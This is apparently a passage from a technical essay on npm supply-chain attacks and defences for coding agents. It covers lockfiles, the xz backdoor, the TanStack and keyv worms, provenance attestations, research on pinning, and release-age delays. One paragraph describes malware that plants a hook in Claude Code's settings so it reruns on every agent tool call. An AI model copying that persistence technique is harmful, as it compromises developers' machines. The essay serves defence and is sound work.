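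An agent that adds a dependency usually gets less protection from the lockfile than the project does, because f for the new package is the moment the agent adds it. An old lockfile still gives partial protection, because npm can reuse versions that the project has already locked. For instance, a project that had already locked a clean `flat-cache` could keep it when the agent added another library that accepted the same version.

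This also limits what a person can learn by looking up a package before approving it. On the morning of 4 August, `keyv` was still a well-known package with an honest maintainer and a long history. These short windows are the main argument for release-age delays.

Once npm removes a malicious archive, `npm ci` fails on any machine that has to download it, even if the lockfile names it. But a harness that prefetched the archive can keep installing its stored copy, and a company mirror can keep serving it. Anyone who stores packages therefore needs a way to check the stored digests against new security advisories.

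### xz and the malicious official release

In the xz case, the release itself was malicious and stayed available for weeks. xz Utils is a set of compression tools that most Linux systems include. A contributor using the name Jia Tan had helped with the project for more than two years and become a maintainer. Tan's release archives for versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1, published in February and March 2024, contained a build script that was not in the project's repository. The script extracted hidden code from test files and added it to the compression library. On some Linux systems, the remote login server loads this library, and the hidden code would have let the holder of a secret key run commands on those machines.

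Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer, found the backdoor because logins were taking half a second longer than they should. He made it public on 29 March, about five weeks after 5.6.0 came out.

A user who had pinned 5.4 was safe, but a user who pinned 5.6.0 on the day of its release would have received the same backdoored bytes every time, with a matching digest. Nobody had stolen an account or moved a tag, so checking the publisher's identity wouldn't have helped either. An installation plan that showed the archive before approval would have let a reader inspect it, but many experienced packagers had access to the same files and didn't find the backdoor. This attack took much longer to prepare than the npm worms, and a fixed payload is a poor defence against it.

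### What a first fetch could have shown

In the TanStack attack, a careful reviewer who inspected the package before running it could have found an unreadable 2.3 MB file named `router_init.js` and the odd Git dependency. The official advisory recommends `npm pack`, which downloads a package's archive without running its install scripts. In the AntV and August attacks, a summary of new install scripts would have shown a `preinstall` command that started a program from inside the package.

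Older versions of npm can run a Git dependency's `prepare` script while still fetching the package, so a harness should refuse to fetch Git dependencies until a person has approved them. Fetching in a container that holds no passwords adds protection, because a credential stealer that runs there has little to take.

Running the code offline after approval would have stopped most of these attacks from sending data out, even if the person approving it had missed every warning sign. A list of allowed sites is weaker protection because the TanStack malware could hide stolen data in GitHub commits, and Snyk's *TanStack npm packages compromised* (2026) notes that network rules on nearly all build servers allow traffic to GitHub.

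If a bad package runs outside a container, returning to a clean lockfile isn't enough, because files the malware changed elsewhere may remain. The TanStack malware also wrote a hook into `.claude/settings.json` so Claude Code would run the malware again whenever the agent used a tool. It added a similar startup task to the settings of VS Code, a code editor. The August worm did the same for Claude Code, VS Code and GitHub Copilot, according to OpenNET. An approval that covers the project's files could detect the hook, but only if the malware can't edit the settings that control the check.

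TanStack's advisory also recommends pinning every TanStack package to a version from before the attack, then deleting the lockfile and reinstalling. This removes a malicious version recorded in the lockfile. But it also makes npm choose new versions for every other floating dependency, and the worm had spread to more than 100 packages from other publishers by the end of that day. A team with a clean lockfile from the previous week could restore that file instead, without changing its other dependencies.

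### What a provenance attestation establishes

npm can publish a provenance attestation with a package, a signed statement of where and how someone built it. On GitHub Actions, the process has four steps:

1. The workflow gets a short-lived token from GitHub that identifies the repository, the workflow and the branch.
2. Sigstore, a public signing service, checks the token and issues a certificate for that identity.
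3. The workflow signs a statement that links the package's digest to the repository, the commit and the workflow.
4. npm makes the statement available beside the package, where anyone can check it.

npm's trusted publishing uses the same kind of token in place of a stored password. A package's owner registers a repository with npm, and npm then accepts releases from its workflow. This takes away the long-lived publishing password that an attacker could otherwise steal, but any code that runs inside the release workflow can use the workflow's identity.

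TanStack's malicious packages had valid attestations because the attackers' code ran in the real release workflow on the project's main branch, and GitHub gave it a genuine token. Snyk points out that the attestations accurately recorded the repository, workflow and branch that had published the packages. They met Build Level 3 of SLSA, a framework that grades how well a build process resists tampering. Snyk describes this as the first documented npm worm to produce such attestations.

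Snyk blames a setting that trusted TanStack's whole repository and advises owners to name one workflow and one branch, but TanStack's account describes a setting that already named both. Either setting would have accepted this attack, because the malicious code ran in the workflow and on the branch that Snyk recommends naming.

The August attackers got their attestations more simply, by adding their files to the project's source repository and making releases through its normal workflow. OSV's *MAL-2026-11971* (2026), an advisory on `flat-cache`, states that provenance "attests build integrity, not source integrity". By the end of August, malicious releases with provenance were no longer unusual. Socket's *OpenAPI React Query Codegen Compromised in Mini Shai-Hulud npm Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports ten malicious versions of another package, all with valid provenance.

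The AntV malware could also obtain genuine certificates when it ran on a victim's build server. The security company Endor Labs, quoted in The Hacker News, explains that such a certificate carries the identity of that server's workflow, even though nobody there had authorised the release.

A harness that shows a green tick for "valid provenance" would therefore mislead the person approving the command. It could instead compare the repository in the attestation with the one used for earlier releases. This would catch an attacker who published from their own machine with a stolen password, or who signed with the identity of an unrelated project. It would not have caught the TanStack or keyv releases, which came from the right repositories.

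The attestation also names a commit, which a reviewer can compare with the package. At TanStack, the release workflow had started from an ordinary bug fix, so the source would have looked harmless, but the package contained an extra 2.3 MB file. A tool could find that difference, but the comparison is noisy because most JavaScript packages contain generated files that are not in the repository. In the keyv attack, the malicious files were also in the source, so the comparison would have found no difference and someone had to read the commit.

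## Does pinning leave software out of date and less safe?

A lockfile written before an attack keeps out the malicious release, but it also keeps out the next bug fix. Any code pinned by an approval likewise becomes outdated over time. Whether this makes software less safe depends partly on which risk its maintainers worry about more, malicious releases or unfixed bugs. Developers and security specialists have argued about this for years.

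### The case for each side

Security specialists who recommend pinning are concerned about malicious releases. He and colleagues cite a survey of 17 experts and 134 developers that ranked pinning among the three best safeguards against supply chain attacks for the effort it takes. Scorecard, a tool that rates the security habits of open-source projects, includes pinned dependencies among its 18 good practices. These specialists mainly argue that malicious releases are more dangerous than accidental flaws, many of which are hard to exploit and never hurt anyone. A malicious release can steal passwords as soon as someone installs it.

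Developers who prefer floating versions worry about accidental flaws, which honest publishers repair in later releases. The rule `^1.2.0` picks up a repaired 1.2.1 at the next resolution, but an exact pin keeps the old version until somebody edits the file, and often nobody does. *On the Freshness of Pinned Dependencies in Maven* (2025) calls a pin stale when a project was released with an old version of a library although a newer one was already out. In a 2020 survey that He and colleagues cite, most npm developers favoured floating versions, although pinning has become more common since then.

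Datadog's *State of DevSecOps* (2026) suggests that both outdated and newly released dependencies carry risks. Across tens of thousands of applications, the median dependency was 278 days behind, up from 215 a year earlier, and 87% of organisations ran at least one service with an exploitable vulnerability. But half of the organisations had used some library within a day of its release, and 1.6% of those using npm had installed at least one malicious package in the past year. Datadog sells security tools and drew these figures from its own customers, so other companies may differ. Exploitable vulnerabilities were far more common than malicious packages, but the figures don't show which does more harm.

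### A simulated year of npm

He and colleagues tested the argument for pinning on 10,000 npm packages and 10,000 GitHub repositories that use npm. They took each project's `package.json` from September 2022 and made a copy without the carets and tildes, so that `^1.2.0` became `1.2.0`. They used npm's `--before` option to resolve both files as npm would have on five dates, 90 days apart, over the following year. Neither file changed during the year, so the copy represents a developer who pins every direct dependency and doesn't update the pins.

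| Average per project | Original rules | Direct dependencies pinned |
|---|---|---|
| Floating rules anywhere in the dependency graph | 432.35 | 427.83 |
| Automatic updates since the start | 30.30 | 24.86 |
| Dependencies with a known vulnerability | 2.13 | 2.70 |
| Outdated direct dependencies | 5.96 | 8.78 |
| Packages present in more than one version | 22.38 | 23.51 |

The top row measures exposure to malicious updates, because any floating rule can let in a new release that no one chose. Pinning removed only about 1% of these rules, since most of them belong to transitive dependencies. It also left projects with 27% more vulnerable dependencies and 47% more outdated ones.

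The averages combine small and large projects, so He and colleagues also fitted a regression. Let F be the number of floating rules, S the number of packages in the graph, and P equal to 1 if the project pins and 0 if it doesn't. The part of the model that depends on pinning is:

ln(F + 1) = … − 0.519 P + 0.084 P ln(S)

Pinning reduces floating rules when 0.084 ln(S) is less than 0.519. The formula gives about 17% fewer floating rules in a graph of 50 packages and about 13% more in a graph of 2,000. With these rounded coefficients, the two terms cancel at roughly 480 packages, while He et al. put the crossover at 498. In their sample, 26% of GitHub repositories had graphs at least that large.

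The study counts openings for attack, not actual attacks. It assumes that attackers are equally likely to choose any package, and it couldn't resolve the dependencies of about one project in seven at past dates. Its vulnerability figures also reflect pins left without updates, so a developer who pins and then updates every month would do better.

### How a pin can add exposure

The increase happens because npm installs two versions of a package when no single version meets every requirement. Suppose a project uses `examplelib` and `examplehttp`, and `examplehttp` needs `examplelib` at `^1.4.0`. The newest `examplelib` is 1.9.0, and every version of it has three dependencies, all with caret ranges.

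| | Project asks for `examplelib` `^1.2.0` | Project pins `examplelib` to 1.2.0 |
|---|---|---|
| Copies of `examplelib` that npm installs | 1.9.0 | 1.2.0 for the project, 1.9.0 for `examplehttp` |
| Floating rules in the project's own file | 2 | 0, because it pins `examplehttp` too |
| Floating rules in `examplehttp` | 1 | 1 |
| Floating rules in the copies of `examplelib` | 3 | 6 |
| Total | 6 | 7 |

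The pin removed two floating rules and added three. If the old copy depends on packages that 1.9.0 no longer uses, the project also trusts additional publishers. Branches of large dependency graphs share more packages, so this can happen in more places.

The reversal is specific to npm. Most other package managers have to find a single version of each package. For those, He and colleagues expect that pinning direct dependencies would also do little to reduce exposure but would not increase it, and that conflicts between pins would be harder to resolve.

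### Lockfiles and the simulation

These results are not evidence against complete lockfiles, because the simulation resolved every transitive dependency again on each date, which `npm ci` never does. With a lockfile, all 432 floating rules in the average project have no effect until somebody updates the lockfile. He et al. advise application developers to commit a lockfile instead of pinning, and 44% of the GitHub repositories in their sample had committed one.

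If an agent replaces `^7.5.0` with `7.5.4` in `package.json` and describes this as a security improvement, the change therefore does very little by itself.

### Pinning by a few central packages

A library can't pass its lockfile on to the projects that install it, so He and colleagues also studied how well a small number of popular packages that lie on many dependency paths could protect the others. They simulated attacks on a network of 1.57 million npm packages. In each attack, the attacker takes over one of the 1,000 packages whose compromise would affect the most downloads. With no defence, an average attack reaches 1.93% of all npm downloads.

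| What the defending packages do | Reduction with 20 packages | Reduction with 100 packages |
|---|---|---|
| Pin their direct dependencies, as npm allows | 12% | 30% |
| Pin their whole graph and pass it to their users | 51% | 76% |

If 100 maintainers pinned their dependencies, the average attack would reach about 1.35% of downloads with ordinary pins, or 0.47% if npm passed pinned dependency graphs downstream. Persuading 100 maintainers is more realistic than persuading a million.

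However, it is optimistic to assume that the defenders review every update immediately and never miss a malicious one, since experienced packagers missed the xz backdoor. Passing on a dependency graph would also make 100 teams responsible for delivering every security fix to everyone downstream. npm 12 has moved in the opposite direction by ignoring lockfiles inside packages.

### What happened to real dependencies

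In *Which Is Better For Reducing Outdated and Vulnerable Dependencies*, Rahman, Marley and colleagues (2025) studied the version rules that publishers actually chose. They followed 16,094 dependencies of highly ranked packages on npm, PyPI and Cargo and recorded when each became outdated or vulnerable. They counted a dependency as vulnerable only if a fixed version was already available.

The results are hazard ratios. A hazard is the rate at which an event happens among the cases where it hasn't happened yet. Each ratio divides the hazard for one kind of rule by the hazard for exact pins. A value below 1 means the rule did better than pinning.

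| Rule | Example | Becoming outdated | Becoming vulnerable |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exact pin | `1.2.0` | 1 | 1 |
| Any later version | `>=1.2.0` | 0.01 | No estimate, because none became vulnerable |
| Minor and patch releases | `^1.2.0` | 0.44 | 0.57 |
| Patch releases only | `~1.2.0` | 0.75 | 1.48 |
| Range with a lower and an upper limit | `>1.2.3 <4.0.0` | 0.62 | 2.69 |

Caret ranges became vulnerable at a 43% lower rate than exact pins, which supports developers who prefer floating versions. But tilde ranges, which also allow more fixes than pins, became vulnerable at a 48% higher rate.

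Rahman and colleagues attribute this to how publishers release fixes. They found 1,553 packages in which a vulnerability affected several major versions but the publisher fixed only one. For example, a flaw in the npm package `dset` affected every version up to 3.1.1, but the publisher released the fix only in 3.1.2, so a project with the rule `^2.0.0` never receives it.

This explains why a floating rule may do no better than a pin, but not why it would do worse. The projects themselves probably account for part of the difference. Developers who set an upper limit have often found something that works and don't want to change it, as the study suggests for bounded ranges. The study also says that caret ranges may do well partly because they are so common in the sample. The ratios therefore describe the kinds of project that use each rule and can't be used to predict what would happen if one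 project changed its rule.

Rahman and colleagues, like He and colleagues, recommend floating version rules with a lockfile. Whether the software stays up to date then depends on how often someone refreshes the lockfile. A lockfile that nobody refreshes for a year misses the same fixes as a year-old pin.

### Release-age delays

Each refresh can bring in a malicious release along with the fixes. A release-age delay, often called a cooldown, makes the resolver ignore versions younger than a set age. If `examplelib` 1.3.0 comes out today and the delay is three days, the rule `^1.2.0` keeps resolving to 1.2.3 until the three days have passed. A malicious release that is removed before the delay ends never reaches the user.

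The recent npm attacks were short enough that waiting before installing new releases would have blocked most of them. *A Difference Without a Distinction* (2026), a study of package registries, reconstructed 41 malicious releases and found that they had stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours. A one-day delay would have kept out 36 of them and a seven-day delay 40. These figures probably overstate the benefit of waiting, because they leave out attacks that nobody has discovered. The backdoored xz release was available for about five weeks, so neither delay would have kept it out.

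A delay also relies on other people finding the problem in the meantime. If every user waited a week, fewer victims would report an attack on the first day. Automatic scanners and researchers can still check new releases immediately, and an outside researcher reported the TanStack attack within half an hour, but nobody has yet seen how detection works when most users delay.

Package managers added these settings quickly. The versions and names below come from Willison's list, *package managers need to cool down* (2026), and mcollina's guide, *Configuring minimum release age across npm, pnpm, and yarn*.

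| Tool | Setting | Available since |
|---|---|---|
| pnpm | `minimumReleaseAge`, in minutes | 10.16, September 2025; one day by default since version 11 |
| Yarn | `npmMinimalAgeGate`, in minutes | 4.10.0, September 2025 |
| Bun | `minimumReleaseAge` | 1.3, October 2025 |
| uv | `--exclude-newer`, with a date or a period such as "1 week" | Periods since 0.9.17, December 2025 |
| Deno | `--minimum-dependency-age`, for its update commands | 2.6, December 2025 |
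| pip | `--uploaded-prior-to` | 26.0, January 2026; periods since 26.1 |
| npm | `min-release-age`, in days | 11.10.0, February 2026 |

By early September 2026, Bundler, Hex, Mamba and mise had similar settings, and Cargo had one in its experimental version, according to *package manager trends* (2026).

The units are easy to confuse. A setting of 7 means a week in npm but seven minutes in pnpm, so an agent that copies it from npm to pnpm can effectively switch off the protection while appearing to keep it. An older version of a tool may also ignore a setting it doesn't support. *package manager trends* mentions an old version of pnpm that did this in a project affected by a compromise of the build tool Nx.

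### How projects use the delay

Dependabot, GitHub's update tool, checks a project's dependencies on a schedule and opens a pull request (a proposed change that somebody has to accept) for each new version. Since July 2025 it has offered the option to delay these pull requests. Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues (2026) examined 1,462 popular repositories that use Dependabot and found that 135 had adopted the delay by the end of April 2026 (*An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects*).

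Two researchers read the commit messages and discussions behind each adoption. They identified a reason in 92 cases, 83 of which involved security. In 43 cases the project was responding to a warning from a security scanner such as zizmor, so many maintainers seem to have accepted a tool's recommendation instead of working out a policy.

The settings also suggest this. Of the 244 configurations with a general delay, 157 used seven days, and fewer than one in ten of all configurations set separate delays for major, minor or patch releases. When projects later changed the general delay, they always raised it from three or four days to seven. No repository removed the delay.

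Tanaka and colleagues didn't measure whether the delay kept out any malicious releases, and they say that the popularity of seven days doesn't show it is the best choice. In August 2026, after the study's cutoff, GitHub gave Dependabot a default delay of three days. In *A Difference Without a Distinction*, the malicious releases whose time online is known lasted at most 2.5 days, so either delay would have outlasted them.

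Dependabot's delay applies only to the updates it proposes. If an agent runs `npm install examplelib` during a task, the package manager could install a release published ten minutes earlier unless it has its own delay.

### Urgent fixes

A delay on new releases holds back fixes as well as attacks. Sharma and colleagues, who built YUL to keep agents on the latest releases, add that an agent may write an old version into a project and run it immediately, and that a delay then keeps the project on that version for several more days. A harness that combined YUL with a delay would also give the agent contradictory instructions, because YUL can require the newest release while the package manager blocks it.

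Update tools commonly exempt security fixes from the delay. Dependabot's default delay doesn't apply to updates that fix a known vulnerability. According to *package manager trends*, Dependabot, Renovate and Hex can all lift the delay when a security advisory covers the version a project currently uses. This depends on someone having written the advisory. Without one, a fix included in an ordinary release is still delayed, as is a release that an attacker merely describes as urgent.

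Tanaka and colleagues found five projects that exempted particular dependencies from pinning. The projects' reasons included getting fixes to cryptographic libraries quickly and trusting packages from their own organisation. The second reason is weaker after the attacks on TanStack and keyv, where the malicious releases came through the publishers' normal channels.

A seven-day delay is short compared with the 278 days by which the median dependency in Datadog's data was behind. Datadog also found that only 18% of vulnerabilities rated critical stayed critical once it accounted for where the software ran and how likely an attack was. For most projects, delaying routine updates by a week adds little risk compared with not updating at all. If attackers are already using a flaw, somebody should override the delay by hand.

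### Updates as separate proposals

Floating rules, a lockfile, a delay and an update tool can be combined so that a project receives fixes without accepting each release automatically:

1. `package.json` states the range of versions that the project accepts.
2. The lockfile fixes the exact versions, and every routine install uses `npm ci`.
3. Dependabot or Renovate waits for the delay to pass, then proposes a change to the lockfile. It proposes security fixes immediately.
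4. The project's tests run on the proposal.
5. A person accepts or rejects it, separately from any other work.

For a coding agent, the important step is keeping package updates separate from other work. An agent fixing a login page has no reason to update forty packages in the same change, and a person approving the page is unlikely to examine them. If the agent proposes `npm update`, the person can decline it and leave the update for its own pull request. An exception is reasonable when the task needs a newer version of a package.

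The tests in step 4 run the new code before anyone has approved it. A malicious release could therefore act on the build server, so the test job should have no access to passwords or publishing tokens.

Dependabot proposed 95,516 version updates in the 1,462 repositories over ten months, an average of about 65 per repository. At 15 minutes per proposal, reviewing them would take about 16 hours for the average repository. Fifteen minutes is enough to read the release notes and check the test results, but usually not to read the changed code, and a single proposal may also update several transitive dependencies. The median was 54 proposals in the repositories that adopted the delay and 19 in the others.

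Older research that Tanaka and colleagues cite found that projects with automated pull requests updated their dependencies 1.6 times as often as projects without them. Developers on the projects with automation merged only about a third of the proposals, which left many that somebody had to look at and then ignore. Their main worries included breaking changes and the difficulty of understanding an update.

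Many maintainers accept proposals quickly. Among repositories that merged any, the median merge time was about 11 hours for those with a delay and 19 hours for those without. These times include nights and waiting, so they don't show how long anyone spent reading. In 20% of the repositories with a delay and 13% of the others, somebody had turned on GitHub's automatic merging for at least one proposal, which leaves the tests as the only check. Malicious code can run without breaking anything, as it did in the Trivy attack, so the tests may still pass.

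A project can reduce the work by accepting patch releases automatically after the delay and having a person review only new packages, new install scripts and major versions. This gives standing approval to code that nobody on the project has read, although only to releases that have been public for a few days. It is probably the safer choice for a small team that would otherwise stop updating.
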